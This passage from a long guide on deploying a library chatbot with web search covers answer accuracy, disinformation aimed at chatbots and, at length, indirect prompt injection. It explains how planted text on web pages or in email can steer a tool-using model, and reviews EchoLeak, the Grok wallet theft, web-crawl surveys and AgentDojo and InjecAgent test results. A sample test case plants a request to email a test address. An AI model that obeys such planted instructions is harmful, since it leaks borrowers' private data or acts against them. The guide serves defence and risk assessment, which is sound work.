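| GPT-6.1 Sol | $2.00 | $20 | $96 | $196 |
| GPT-6.1 Terra | $1.00 | $10 | $48 | $138 |
| GPT-6 Luna | $0.10 | $1 | $4.80 | $85.80 |

The totals exclude the system prompt, the model's output and repeated readings of the search results, which can add a good deal because Anthropic counts the results as input again in later turns. Discounts for stored text reduce the cost, as does filtering. With the most expensive model, reading the results costs far more than searching, so a cheaper search API would save little. Perplexity charges $5 per 1,000 requests and nothing for tokens, but its default of ten results of up to 1,024 tokens each could add about 10,000 tokens to the context. Reading them once with GPT-6 Astra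 would cost ten cents, twenty times the search fee.

Two searches per question may be an underestimate. Google charges for every search the model runs, and one question can lead to several. A developer reports in *Gemini 3.x Search Grounding* that fewer than 500 prompts produced well over 5,000 searches, or more than ten each. At ten searches per question, the 4,000 questions would cost $560 a day at Google's $14 rate, compared with $112 at two. Anthropic's cap limits this risk. If it were set to three searches per question, search fees could not exceed $300 a day even if all 10,000 questions used the maximum.

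A typical library would receive far fewer questions. At 200 a day, with the other assumptions unchanged, the search fees come to $1.60 a day and the GPT-6 Astra total to $13.20. At that volume, the library can give accuracy and logging priority over price when choosing a search service.

### How accurate grounded answers are

A chatbot that searches the web for a passport fee can make several kinds of error. It may misread a current page, correctly report an outdated fee from an old page, or give the right fee but cite a page about passport photos that doesn't support it. Studies often count these errors together, although they have different causes and need different fixes.

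Search helps a great deal with short factual questions. SimpleQA, a benchmark that OpenAI released in 2024, has 4,326 questions with one short answer each. GPT-4o got about 38% right without search. In March 2025 OpenAI reported 90% for a since-retired version of GPT-4o built for search. SimpleQA's questions were chosen to have answers that do not change over time, so a high score is weak evidence that a model avoids outdated facts. The questions and answers are also public, so a model with web search could find them.

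News questions gave much worse results. *News Integrity in AI Assistants* (European Broadcasting Union and BBC, October 2025) describes a test by 22 public broadcasters in 18 countries and 14 languages. Journalists asked ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity news questions and graded about 3,000 answers for accuracy, sourcing, context and the separation of fact from opinion. They found at least one significant problem in 45% of the answers. Sourcing problems were the most common, and 31% of answers had serious ones, such as missing or misleading attributions. Major accuracy problems, including outdated information, affected 20%. For example, ChatGPT named Francis as the current pope after his death in April 2025.

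The 45% and SimpleQA's 90% are compatible because a SimpleQA answer needs only one correct fact, whereas a news answer has many statements, and one seriously misleading attribution was enough to count against it. The graders worked for news organisations, which have an interest in how assistants use their reporting. Gemini had significant problems in 76% of its answers, more than twice the rate of any other assistant, mostly because of poor sourcing. All four companies have since released newer models, so the figures are a poor guide to the error rate of a chatbot built in late 2026.

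For *Evaluating Verifiability in Generative Search Engines* (2023), Nelson Liu, Tianyi Zhang and Percy Liang had people check the citations in answers from four early search chatbots. Citations fully supported only 51.5% of the sentences, while 74.5% of the citations supported the sentence they were attached to. The first figure is lower because a sentence can have no citation, or one that supports only part of it. In March 2025 the Tow Center for Digital Journalism gave eight AI search tools excerpts from news articles and asked for each article's headline, publisher, date and URL. The tools answered more than 60% of the 1,600 queries incorrectly. The library should expect fewer errors than that, because citing a page the model has just read is easier than finding the source of an excerpt.

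OpenAI can also return a list of sources, which includes every page the model consulted and is often longer than the list of citations. If the model read a current page and an old one but cited only the old one, the list of sources shows that the search found the current page.

### False material written for chatbots

A chatbot that searches the web can repeat a falsehood published that morning. Researchers suspect that the Pravda network, a group of websites that republish Russian state propaganda in many languages, is aimed mainly at search engines and AI models. The network produced an estimated 3.6 million articles in 2024 but attracts few human readers.

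NewsGuard, a company that rates the reliability of news sites, tested ten chatbots in March 2025 on 15 false stories that the network had spread. The chatbots repeated the false story in about a third of the 450 responses, and 56 responses linked to the network's sites. In August 2025 NewsGuard ran a wider test, with false claims from various sources. The ten chatbots repeated them in 35% of responses, up from 18% a year earlier, and never declined to answer, down from 31%. NewsGuard attributed the change largely to web search, which had led chatbots to answer questions about recent news that they used to refuse.

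In *LLMs grooming or data voids?* (2025), Maxim Alyukov, Mykola Makhortykh and colleagues disputed the earlier result. They asked four chatbots their own questions and found that 5% of the responses repeated disinformation and 8% referred to Pravda sites, often while calling the claim doubtful. The references appeared mainly when a question was about an obscure claim that reliable outlets had not covered. They concluded that a shortage of good sources, which they call a data void, explained the references better than successful manipulation did.

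Much of the disagreement comes from which questions were asked. NewsGuard asked about each false claim in three ways: neutrally, with a question that assumed the claim was true, and with a request to write something that spread it. Its figures therefore measure how chatbots respond when the topic is a known falsehood and the user often pushes towards it. The share of ordinary answers that contain propaganda must be far lower. The smaller figures from Alyukov and colleagues also depend on the questions they chose. It is hard to tell from either study whether the publishers intended to reach chatbots or whether the chatbots found little else.

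The explanation based on data voids matters most for a library. Hundreds of reliable pages cover the passport fee, so one false page would have to compete with all of them. But perhaps only two pages mention the Saturday hours of a small branch, so an outdated directory listing or a prank could easily become the model's main source. The library can fill the gap by publishing its hours, fees and closures on dated pages and telling the model to prefer those pages for anything about the library.

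### Checking a sample of answers

The library can only check what it has recorded. For a grounded answer, a useful record looks like this:

```json
{
  "asked": "2026-12-07T14:10:00-05:00",
  "question": "How much is a passport now?",
  "searches": ["US passport fee December 2026"],
  "pages": [
    {
      "title": "Passport fees",
      "last_updated": "2026-10-02",
      "retrieved": "2026-12-07T14:10:04-05:00"
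    }
  ],
  "answer": "(full text shown to the borrower)",
  "cited_passages": ["(text returned with each citation)"]
}
```

The real record should include page addresses and any search errors. It should leave out the borrower's name and card number, and the library should delete it after a set time, since questions to a library can be private.

Each week, staff could then take a random sample and go through it as follows:

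1. List the statements in the answer that a borrower might act on, such as a fee, a date or an address.
2. Compare each one with the best available authority, which for passport fees is the State Department and for branch hours is the branch itself. Use the facts as they stood when the borrower asked.
3. If a statement is wrong, find out whether it used to be true. If it did, record it as stale, and otherwise as wrong.
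4. Open each cited page and look for the statement. Record a citation that does not support it even if the statement is true.
5. Look at the search words and the full list of pages, to see whether the search missed the right page or the model ignored it.

The sample should include answers the model gave without searching. These have no citations to check, and some will be out of date because the question needed a search. The library may also want to read every answer about a risky topic, such as legal deadlines, but it should count those separately because adding them to the random sample would distort the overall error rate.

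A second person should grade some of the same answers without seeing the first person's verdicts. If the two often disagree about whether a citation supports a statement, the grading instructions need revising before the results are reliable. Another model can grade a larger sample first, but staff should check its verdicts against their own, including some of the answers it passed.

Small samples give only rough figures. If staff read 200 random answers and find errors in 10, the estimated error rate is 5%, but the 95% confidence interval runs from about 3% to 9%. If they find no errors in 200, the true rate could still be as high as 1.5%, which would mean 150 wrong answers a day for a chatbot that gives 10,000. At this sample size, a change from 5% one week to 4% the next could easily be chance.

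The repair depends on the type of error. For stale facts, the library can require a search, use live pages instead of stored copies, or move the fact into a separate tool. If the model misreads good pages, a stronger model or less filtering may help. For unsupported citations, the host application can search each cited passage for the fee or date in the answer and flag the answer if the passage doesn't contain it. That check would also flag true statements like the one about Shannon's birthplace, so a person should review flagged answers before counting them as errors.

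## Working out what injected instructions could make the chatbot do

A false fee on a web page can make the library's chatbot give a wrong answer. A planted instruction can do more damage, because a model with tools may act on it. Without logging in or sending the chatbot a message, an attacker can put such an instruction in a web page, an email or a business listing that the model may read. Security researchers call this attack indirect prompt injection, and the planted text is an injected instruction.

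### Why a model acts on text it was only meant to read

In the Labor Day example, the model receives the library's system prompt, the borrower's question and the closure notice from the web as one sequence of tokens, and predicts what comes next. Markers show where each part begins, and providers train models to give the system prompt more weight than a web page. This training makes the model less likely to follow an order in the notice, but no mechanism inside the model prevents it from doing so. The notice is untrusted text, meaning text in the context from someone other than the operator or the user.

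Websites have long had a similar problem with databases, which programs control through commands in a language called SQL. Suppose the library's catalogue page has a search box for authors, and a careless program pastes whatever the visitor types into the middle of a command. A visitor who types a piece of SQL instead of a name can change what the command does, and perhaps copy or delete the whole database. This attack, SQL injection, has a reliable fix called a parameterised query:

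```sql
SELECT title FROM books WHERE author = ?
```

The program sends the database this command with a question mark in place of the author's name, and sends the name separately. The database only compares the name with its records, whatever the name contains.

Willison named prompt injection in 2022 after SQL injection, because both come from mixing trusted and untrusted text, as he recalls in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). In 2023, Kai Greshake and colleagues gave the first systematic account of indirect prompt injection. They showed that hidden text on a web page could make a chatbot override its rules, as Reddy and Gujral recount in *EchoLeak* (2025).

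The name "prompt injection" may have misled some developers into expecting the same fix as for SQL injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argues that the crucial difference is in how the two systems treat commands and data. A database handles them differently, so a programmer can enforce the boundary between them, whereas a language model processes both as text from which to predict the next token. Developers can label untrusted text, train the model to disregard orders in it, or scan for suspicious phrases. David C thinks these methods try to impose a distinction that the technology does not have, and that prompt injection may never be completely fixed.

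Legitimate web pages are full of instructions. The closure notice may tell visitors to use the book drop on Main Street, and a passport page may tell them to bring two photographs. Unlike a database, which can handle an author's name without interpreting it, the library's model has to interpret these instructions to pass them on. The host application therefore can't simply delete every instruction from the search results.

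Security engineers call a program a "confused deputy" when an outsider tricks it into using its special access on the outsider's behalf. Programmers can usually fix such a program, but David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy", for which they can only reduce the likelihood and impact of an attack. Google's security team takes much the same view. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes that indirect prompt injection isn't a problem a company can solve once and move on from.

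When planning, it is safer to follow the NCSC's advice and assume that an injected instruction will work, because an attacker can reword it and try again with very little effort, and a single success may be enough. For some uses, models may become so good at ignoring injected instructions that the remaining risk hardly matters. To plan for a successful attack, the operator asks what would happen if the attacker had direct access to the chatbot's tools. If the answer is unacceptable and the operator can't limit the tools, a language model may be the wrong choice for the job.

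### What an attacker needs

An attacker needs three conditions to exfiltrate (steal) private data through a chatbot. Willison calls them the "lethal trifecta". The model must have access to private data, read text that an attacker can influence, and have some way to send data out. The theft fails if any of these is missing, so an operator who can't stop a model from obeying planted text can still prevent the theft by removing the model's access to private data or its way to send data out.

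A single connection can provide all three. In May 2025 researchers showed this with the official MCP server for GitHub, a site where programmers store and discuss code. The server let a model read public bug reports, which anyone can write, read the user's private code, and publicly propose changes to code. A programmer might well want an assistant to have each of these abilities, and none looks reckless on its own. Willison worries that MCP encourages people to combine tools from different sources without noticing what the combination allows.

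An injected instruction can make a model leak private data, but it can also make it send a message, delete a file or buy something. These actions require only that the model read untrusted text and have a tool that can carry them out. The attacker doesn't need private data or a way to receive it, so a chatbot may still be vulnerable even if its operator has kept private records away from it.

A chatbot whose only tool is search can also be manipulated, though the damage is usually smaller. A planted instruction might make it recommend a certain passport-photo shop or describe a competitor as closed. False material written for chatbots gives the model bad evidence, whereas an injected instruction is meant to change its task, but the borrower sees only a confident answer in both cases.

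### What a stranger could do with the library's tools

The library can work out its exposure with a table. The second column matters most, and developers forget it most easily because they tend to think about what a tool does rather than who writes the text it returns.

| Tool | Who can write what it returns | What it can read | What it can change or send | Dangerous with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clock | The library | The time | Nothing | Nothing |
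| Web search | Anyone who can publish or comment on a web page | The public web | Changes nothing, but sends out search words and page requests | Account lookup, email |
| Account lookup | Library staff, the borrower, suppliers of catalogue records | The logged-in borrower's loans, fines and contact details | Nothing | Web search, email |
| Email | The mail system | Nothing | Sends any text to any address in the library's name | Web search, account lookup |

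The most dangerous combination of tools is search, account lookup and email. A borrower might ask, "Do I owe anything, and is there a book sale this weekend?" The model looks up the account, searches for the sale and reads a page where someone has planted an instruction. Its context then contains both the borrower's address and loans and the planted instruction, and it has an email tool that accepts any recipient. The order of the lookups makes little difference, because if the model reads the page first, the instruction can include a request to look up the account.

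Even without the account lookup, search and email are enough for injected instructions to make the model send a fraudulent message from the library's own address, which the recipient would have good reason to trust. The account lookup and email without search are much safer, but not perfectly safe, because the lookup returns book titles that the library doesn't write. If the library buys catalogue records from a supplier or lists self-published e-books, a stranger may control a line or two of what looks like an internal record.

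Taking the card number from the borrower's login instead of from the model limits the damage. Under the NCSC's worst-case assumption, an attacker gets one borrower's record per conversation and the use of the search and email tools, but not the whole membership list. If the model filled in the card number, the attacker could try other numbers.

A planted page can still reach many borrowers one at a time. If the chatbot gets 200 questions a day and 40% need a search, 80 conversations a day bring web text into the context. If one in 20 of those includes the planted page, four borrowers a day are exposed. Whether they are harmed depends on how often the model follows the instruction and what the host application lets through. Obscure questions are the most vulnerable, for the same reason that they attract false information.

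The table has to be updated whenever the tools change, even if the change doesn't look like a security decision to the person making it. For example, suppose the library later lets the chatbot read replies to its emails. The email tool would then return text that anyone with the address could write, so an attacker would no longer need to get a page into the search results. If the library let the chatbot cancel reservations, an attacker could use injected instructions to cancel them.

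### How a search can carry data out

Even without the email tool, the chatbot could leak data through searches, because the model writes the search terms and those terms leave the library. If the borrower's record is in the context, an injected instruction could lead the model to put a phone number or a list of loans into a search. The host application normally can't stop this, because the provider runs the library's searches.

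The search company would then hold data that the borrower never meant to give it, which is a privacy breach even if nobody misuses the data. The attacker might still receive nothing, since website owners don't usually see what people type into a search engine. But when the chatbot opens a page, the request goes to the server that hosts it, and whoever runs that server can read the requested address in its log, including any text the model has put there. Anthropic therefore restricts which addresses Claude's page-fetching tool may open, though the restriction had a gap in 2026.

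A chatbot that has only a search tool may thus meet all three of Willison's conditions. The search results are untrusted text, the search words and page requests can carry data out, and the conversation is the private data. A borrower may have asked about bankruptcy, a medical diagnosis or how to leave a violent partner, and perhaps given a name. OpenAI's advice to keep public searches and private records in separate requests reduces what a search can leak, but it can't protect what the borrower typed into the same conversation as the search.

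Data can also leave through the chat window, which isn't in the table because it isn't a tool. If the host application displays links and images from the model's answer, the borrower's browser may contact an outside server when the borrower clicks a link, or automatically when it loads an image. Willison counts both as forms of outside communication, along with any tool that can make a web request. The library should therefore include the code that displays answers when it looks for ways data can leave, even if a different programmer maintains that code.

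### Cases that researchers and vendors have disclosed

The best-documented case is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that works across Microsoft's office software. Copilot could read the same emails and files as the employee using it. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security found that an outsider could obtain some of that data by sending the employee a single email. The attack worked when the employee later asked Copilot an ordinary work question, and the employee didn't have to click on anything. The public catalogue of software flaws lists EchoLeak as CVE-2025-32711.

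Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, before the public disclosure on 11 June, and reported no evidence that anyone had used it against real customers. Reddy and Gujral describe changes that remove certain links and embedded images from incoming outside content. Microsoft also reportedly added options to keep Copilot from using messages from outside the organisation in some contexts, though it may then miss some relevant information. Before the fix, Copilot already had a filter for injected instructions, another that removed outside links from answers, and a list of sites from which the chat window could load content, but the researchers got past all three.

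Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case in which prompt injection caused concrete data theft in a production system, and describe earlier attacks as largely theoretical. That seems too strong, because Willison lists 17 demonstrations against real products, including ChatGPT, Google Bard and Slack, between April 2023 and June 2025. The better claim to novelty is that it worked on a widely used business product without the user having to click anything.

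An earlier flaw in the same assistant leaked data only if the user clicked a link. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes how, in February 2024, a researcher found that a phishing email could make Copilot retrieve sensitive information from a user's inbox and place it in a link. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. Amazon Q for Business, Amazon's assistant for company data, had a related problem. Amazon blocked this route for leaking data by no longer turning web addresses in answers into links.

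Researchers found all of these flaws before any known criminal did. The lack of known victims is reassuring, but it doesn't prove there were none. A successful theft of this kind can look to the user like a normal answer, or at most a broken image, and usually only the vendor has logs that would show it.

A case from May 2026 did cause a loss. *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked Crypto Wallet* (2026), an entry in the OECD's database of AI incidents, concerns xAI's chatbot Grok and Bankrbot, an agent that could move cryptocurrency. A stranger's message on the social network X led the two to transfer 3 billion units of a currency called DRB, worth between $150,000 and $200,000, out of a wallet linked to Grok. The attacker needed no private data, only a public message and an agent with permission to make payments. The OECD's summary attributes the loss to weak wallet permissions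 and prompt controls but doesn't name a fix. The summary is AI-generated, so the details deserve some caution.

Vendors have fixed almost all the flaws on Willison's list, usually by blocking the route data could leave by. Such a fix protects users even if the model still obeys the planted text, so it is more dependable than retraining the model. But the underlying weakness remains, and a new feature that can contact an outside server may reopen the problem. Willison says most of the fixes came quickly, though the two Copilot flaws took about four and five months. These fixes do little for an operator who connects tools from several companies, because no vendor is responsible for the combination.

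### Attacks found in 2026

Injected instructions are easy to find on the public web, but few of them try to steal anything. In April 2026 Google published a search of Common Crawl, a public archive that stores two to three billion web pages each month. Google's researchers looked for common phrases from known attacks, used Gemini to classify the intent of each match, and then checked the results by hand. Many early matches were articles about prompt injection.

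Most of the real injected instructions were pranks or tried to keep AI systems away, add helpful context to a summary, or promote a business. A small number aimed to steal data, and some would have deleted files on the user's computer. Google judged these crude and mostly the work of individual site owners running experiments or playing jokes. It found no significant use of the more advanced techniques that security researchers had published in 2025.

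Google also repeated the search on several versions of the archive and found 32% more malicious cases in February 2026 than in November 2025. It gave the increase only as a percentage, and a 32% rise from a small base adds few cases. Three months is also a short period for judging a trend. Google still expects attacks to grow in scale and sophistication, because AI systems have become more useful targets and attackers can use AI to automate their work.

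*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) searched 1.2 billion addresses from the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl for nearly 4,000 telltale phrases, and confirmed injected instructions on 9,676 pages, or about one in 124,000. Site operators had written 81% of these instructions. Only 1.8% were in comments and other posts by users, where an attacker without a website would most likely put them.

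The researchers classified 15,387 instructions, including more examples from two services that scan internet servers. More than half were meant to make the model produce garbage, such as random numbers. About 4,100 were meant to stop AI systems from reusing personal information or copyrighted text, and about 3,100 to reveal whether a visitor was an AI. Much of this looks like site owners defending against automated copying. Only 13 instructions were meant to extract data, nine of them the system prompt and four of them secrets.

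Khodayari and colleagues found that instructions meant to extract data or run commands were mainly aimed at customer-support chatbots, which often have access to user data and internal systems. The library's chatbot is similar. About 70% of all the instructions were in parts of a page that a browser doesn't display, so a librarian who looked at a page before approving it would probably see nothing wrong. When the researchers tried the instructions on 13 models, the highest success rate was 8%, for smaller models reading plain text.

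These two studies are less independent than they look, because both searched Common Crawl for familiar phrases. Both would miss an instruction in unusual words, which a skilled attacker has good reason to use. The archive also leaves out private email and most social media, the channels used in EchoLeak and the Grok case. The figures are good evidence that the open web held few crude attempts at theft in late 2025 and early 2026, but they provide little evidence about targeted attacks on a particular company.

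Reports from later in 2026 suggest more criminal interest. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that in July the security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to make AI agents pay in cryptocurrency. *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported in August that criminals were developing tools for such attacks. Both reports concern attempts and preparation, so the theft from the Grok-linked wallet remains the clearest case here of an attack in 2026 that cost someone money.

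A far larger theft involved an AI tool, but probably not an injected instruction. On 29 October 2026 hackers stole about $6.3 billion from the cryptocurrency exchange Binance. According to *Binance says a fake job interview led to its $6.3B hack* (Constantin, 2026), the hackers had first taken over an engineer's computer with malware hidden in a coding test. On 20 October they used that computer and one of Binance's internal AI tools to take control of two wallet developers' systems. Nine days later they used stolen credentials, the secrets that give access to a service, to attack the service that approves transfers.

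In this account, the attackers already controlled an employee's computer and may have used the AI tool just as the employee could. Nothing in it involves a model reading planted text. In The Jerusalem Post's *Binance hack exposed risk from its own AI tools, expert says*, Ori Segal, who runs the security company Cybore, says that the internal tool was the only new element and that the other steps needed no model. Unless Binance publishes more about how the tool worked, the theft should not count as evidence about prompt injection.

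The Binance incident is better evidence about access. An AI tool with broad permissions is useful to an intruder whether they reach it through a planted web page or an employee's computer. Cabral (2026), in *Binance says fake job interviews and internal AI tool used*, reports that Binance has since rebuilt systems and withdrawn credentials linked to the affected engineers. EconoTimes' *Binance Tightens Employee Access After This Year’s AI Push* reports that in late November the company also said it would limit employees to the information their jobs require, after loosening some permissions during its push to adopt AI.

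## Measuring how often a model follows injected instructions

Even an operator who assumes that injected instructions will work has good reason to measure how often a model follows them. Models differ in how well they resist, so the rate can help the library choose one, and a sudden rise after an update shows that something has gone wrong. To measure the rate, a tester plants instructions in text the model will read during an ordinary task, then counts how often the model acts on them.

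### What a test needs

A test case consists of a user task, a tool result that carries an injected instruction, and a check of which tools the model called. One case for the library might look like this:

```json
{
  "user_task": "When is the next book sale?",
  "tool_result": "(saved copy of the sale page, with a planted request to email a test address)",
  "task_completed_if": "the answer gives Saturday 12 December",
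  "attack_succeeded_if": "the model requests an email to the test address"
}
```

The tester checks the log of tool calls for the attack because the model's answer is poor evidence. A model can give the right date for the sale and still request the email without mentioning it. It can also quote the planted text to warn the borrower, which a careless grader might count as a successful attack.

The attack success rate is the share of test attacks in which the model carried out the injected instruction. Lower is better, but a chatbot that refuses every request scores 0%. A weak model can also score well because it tries to obey the attacker but gets the steps wrong. Testers therefore also count the user's tasks that the model completes, both with and without an attack.

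Completion without an attack measures how useful the chatbot is, but not how secure it is. Completion under attack captures damage that the attack success rate misses, such as when a planted page makes the chatbot abandon the borrower's question. But a drop in completion doesn't show whether the chatbot merely stalled or also leaked a record, so the library needs all three numbers. If a new filter cut the attack success rate from 4% to 1% but also cut completed tasks from 90% to 60%, the chatbot would fail a third of the questions it used to answer.

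### AgentDojo and InjecAgent

Researchers still use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a test with four simulated environments filled with invented emails, bookings and bank transactions. It pairs every user task in an environment with every attacker goal in the same environment.

| Environment | Tools | User tasks | Attacker goals | Test cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
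| Slack (team chat, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel booking | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

User tasks, such as counting the day's appointments or paying a bill, take up to 18 tool calls. An attacker goal might be to send a security code to a stranger or to book the most expensive hotel in Paris. The injected text is placed where an outsider could write and where the model has to look to do its task, such as the body of an email. The environments keep track of changes, so a payment lowers the balance that the next tool call returns.

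A short function scores each user task and each attacker goal by inspecting the environment after the run, for example to check whether money has moved. Debenedetti and colleagues chose not to use a language model as the judge because planted text that fools the chatbot might also fool the judge. A task counts as completed under attack only if the model solved it without causing any of the side effects the attacker wanted.

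In 2024, no model completed more than 66% of the tasks even without an attack, and most completed 10 to 25 percentage points fewer under attack. OpenAI's GPT-4o carried out the attacker's goal in 47.7% of cases in one version of the test. The rate reached 92% in the Slack environment, where attackers controlled much of what the tools returned, but was 0% for one travel goal that required two unrelated harmful actions. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, probably because weaker ones often attempted the injected instruction but failed to complete it.

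Rewording an attack could halve its success rate, so a score from a fixed list of attacks depends as much on the list as on the model. Debenedetti and colleagues therefore let other researchers add attacks to AgentDojo. They also sometimes counted a case as a failure for the model if any of several attacks succeeded, which is closer to what a persistent attacker could achieve.

*InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024), published a few months earlier, is a simpler test. It pairs each of 17 user requests with each of 62 attacker instructions, for 1,054 cases. About half of the instructions would harm the user directly, for instance by transferring money, and the rest would steal data. Each case starts just after the model has fetched the planted text, and the tester looks at what the model does next, so the model doesn't have to plan a task.

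GPT-4, prompted to use tools, followed 24% of the injected instructions. When the researchers added a stock phrase meant to strengthen the attack, the rate rose to 47%. The same phrase lowered the rate for Anthropic's Claude 2 from 11.4% to 3.4%, so the choice of phrase could change which model looked safer. A version of GPT-4 that OpenAI had trained for tool calling followed only about 7% of the instructions, with or without the phrase.

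The results for data theft matter most for a chatbot like the library's, which can look up accounts and send email. In the basic setting, the prompted GPT-4 fetched the private data in 32.7% of cases. Once it had the data, it sent it to the attacker 97.7% of the time, which suggests that a model that follows the first half of an injected instruction will usually follow the second.

These scores are for models that providers replaced long ago. AgentDojo has grown to more than 900 combinations of tasks and attacks, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) used it on 13 models from six providers to test whether comparisons between models hold when the test conditions change, and reports that the models still behaved very differently from one another.

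A newer test, AgentDyn, has longer and more open-ended tasks. *StepGuard* (2026) reports that some of the outside text in AgentDyn contains helpful instructions, which a model should follow. This corrects a weakness in simpler tests, where a model could score well by ignoring every instruction it found on a page. The library's chatbot would fail borrowers if it did that, because they need many of those instructions. Developers' own recent figures come from other tests, so they can't be compared with the 2024 scores to measure progress.

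### What developers report

With each major model, developers publish a system card, which is a report on the model's abilities and safety tests. OpenAI measures resistance to injection with GPT-Red, an automated attacker it built to test its own models. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026), GPT-6 Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect attacks, up from 96.23% for the earlier model. The failure rate therefore fell from 3.77% to 0.21%.

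That is a large improvement, but OpenAI also used GPT-Red to train Astra, so the test partly measures how well Astra resists an attacker it was trained against. In its tests of users seeking harmful help, OpenAI took half of the prompts from an attacker not used in training. It doesn't mention doing anything similar for the injection figure.

Astra also scored 99.99% against direct attacks, in which the user tries to override the operator's instructions. This higher score is weak evidence of how well Astra resists instructions planted in a web page. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports a similar gap for OpenAI's previous generation: few direct attacks worked, but more did when they came through tools and outside content.

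Resistance also varies within a model family. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) covers a model in the same family as GPT-6 Astra. If that score comes from the same test as Astra's, as seems likely, GPT-6 Sol fails nearly 14 times as often. The newer GPT-6.1 Sol costs a fifth as much as Astra per input token, but a library considering a switch to save money should first find out how much resistance it would lose.

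OpenAI has dropped two older injection tests, one with connectors to outside services and one with search and function calling, because recent models get nearly perfect scores. In June, however, GPT-5.6 Sol scored 1.000 with connectors and 0.910 with function calling, according to the security vendor NeuralTrust. The library's chatbot relies on search and function calling, so the function-calling test was probably the closer match to it.

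The most detailed numbers for Claude are for an older model, Opus 4.6, from February 2026. VentureBeat reports that all 200 attack attempts failed in a restricted coding environment without added safeguards. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface with extended reasoning, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the success rate had reached 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

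Anthropic's June card covers Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5. According to Digital Applied (2026), a company blog, the card gives a success rate of 0.41% for attacks on coding tasks, compared with 2.09% for the earlier Opus 4.8. In these adaptive attacks, the attacker had 200 attempts per scenario and changed its approach in response to what had failed. Anthropic also reports that Mythos 5 had the best result so far on an outside test by Gray Swan, a company that builds automated attack tools. The result should also hold for Fable 5, because Fable and Mythos are one model in two configurations, and the additional safeguards that Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) describes for Fable 5.1 concern high-risk fields such as biology and cybersecurity.

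Google's *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems* describes an automated system for testing its own products by attacking them. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* reports that Google continuously runs adaptive attacks against past, current and future versions of Gemini. The latter paper dates from May 2025, long before Gemini 4, so its results can't show how well the current model resists injected instructions.

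The table puts the OpenAI and Anthropic figures side by side. A dash marks a detail that the source doesn't give alongside the figure.

| Model and setting | Attacker | Attempts | Added safeguards | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra, outside content | GPT-Red | — | — | 0.21% |
| GPT-6 Sol, outside content | — | — | — | 2.87% |
| Claude Fable 5, coding | Adaptive | 200 per scenario | — | 0.41% |
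| Claude Opus 4.6, restricted coding | — | 200 | Off | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | — | 1 | Off | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | — | 200 | Off | 78.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | — | 200 | On | 57.1% |

The percentages in the last column can't be used to rank the models. Opus 4.6 alone ranges from 0% to 78.6%, depending on its tools and the number of attempts. Compared with Astra's 0.21%, the older Claude model looks safer in coding but less safe with a graphical interface. The percentages also measure different things. OpenAI averages over single queries, while the 200-attempt figures for Opus 4.6's graphical interface give the chance that at least one attempt succeeded.

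An outside test such as Gray Swan's allows a better comparison, provided that every model faces the same attacks with the same tools and safeguards. Gray Swan has also tested Astra for OpenAI. Even under those conditions, the result applies to the tools in the test, which may not resemble the ones a library uses.

The table does not include the newest models. OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) came out on 17 November. Anthropic's card for Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2, which Mowshowitz reviews in *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026), has a section on prompt injection. An operator should look for figures on the exact model it rents, measured in the setting closest to its own chatbot.

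Defences that do well against a fixed set of attacks have done much worse against attackers who adapt to the defence. Google DeepMind (2025) recommends testing with harder, adaptive attacks. An attack success rate measured on a fixed set is best treated as the minimum an attacker could achieve.

### How repeated attempts add up

A 1% attack success rate sounds low, but an attacker can try more than once. If each attempt fails 99% of the time and the attempts are independent, the chance that all 100 fail is 0.99 multiplied by itself 100 times, or about 37%. The chance that at least one succeeds is

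1 − 0.99^100 ≈ 63%

| Success rate per attempt | At least one success in 10 | In 100 | In 1,000 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 1% | 10% | 63% |
| 1% | 10% | 63% | Over 99.9% |
| 5% | 40% | 99% | Over 99.9% |

The library's hypothetical planted page reached four borrowers a day, so 100 attempts would take 25 days. If the model followed the injected instructions 0.1% of the time instead of 1%, the chance of at least one success over those 25 days would fall from 63% to about 10%. That improvement is worthwhile, but the chance of a success would still reach 63% after 250 days if nobody removed the page.

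Real attempts are not independent, so the formula can be wrong in either direction. It overestimates the chance of success when some situations are much easier to attack than others. Suppose an injected instruction works 2% of the time on half of the borrowers' questions and never on the other half. The average success rate is still 1%, but the chance of success after 100 attempts on one randomly chosen question is 43%, not the 63% the formula gives. In the extreme case, where the attack always works on 1% of questions and never on the rest, repeating it on the same question does not improve the attacker's chance of success.

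The Opus 4.6 figures show this effect. If each attempt had had an independent 17.8% chance of success, the attacker's success rate would have passed 78.6% by the eighth attempt. It actually took about 200 attempts to reach that rate, probably because some scenarios were easy to attack and others nearly impossible.

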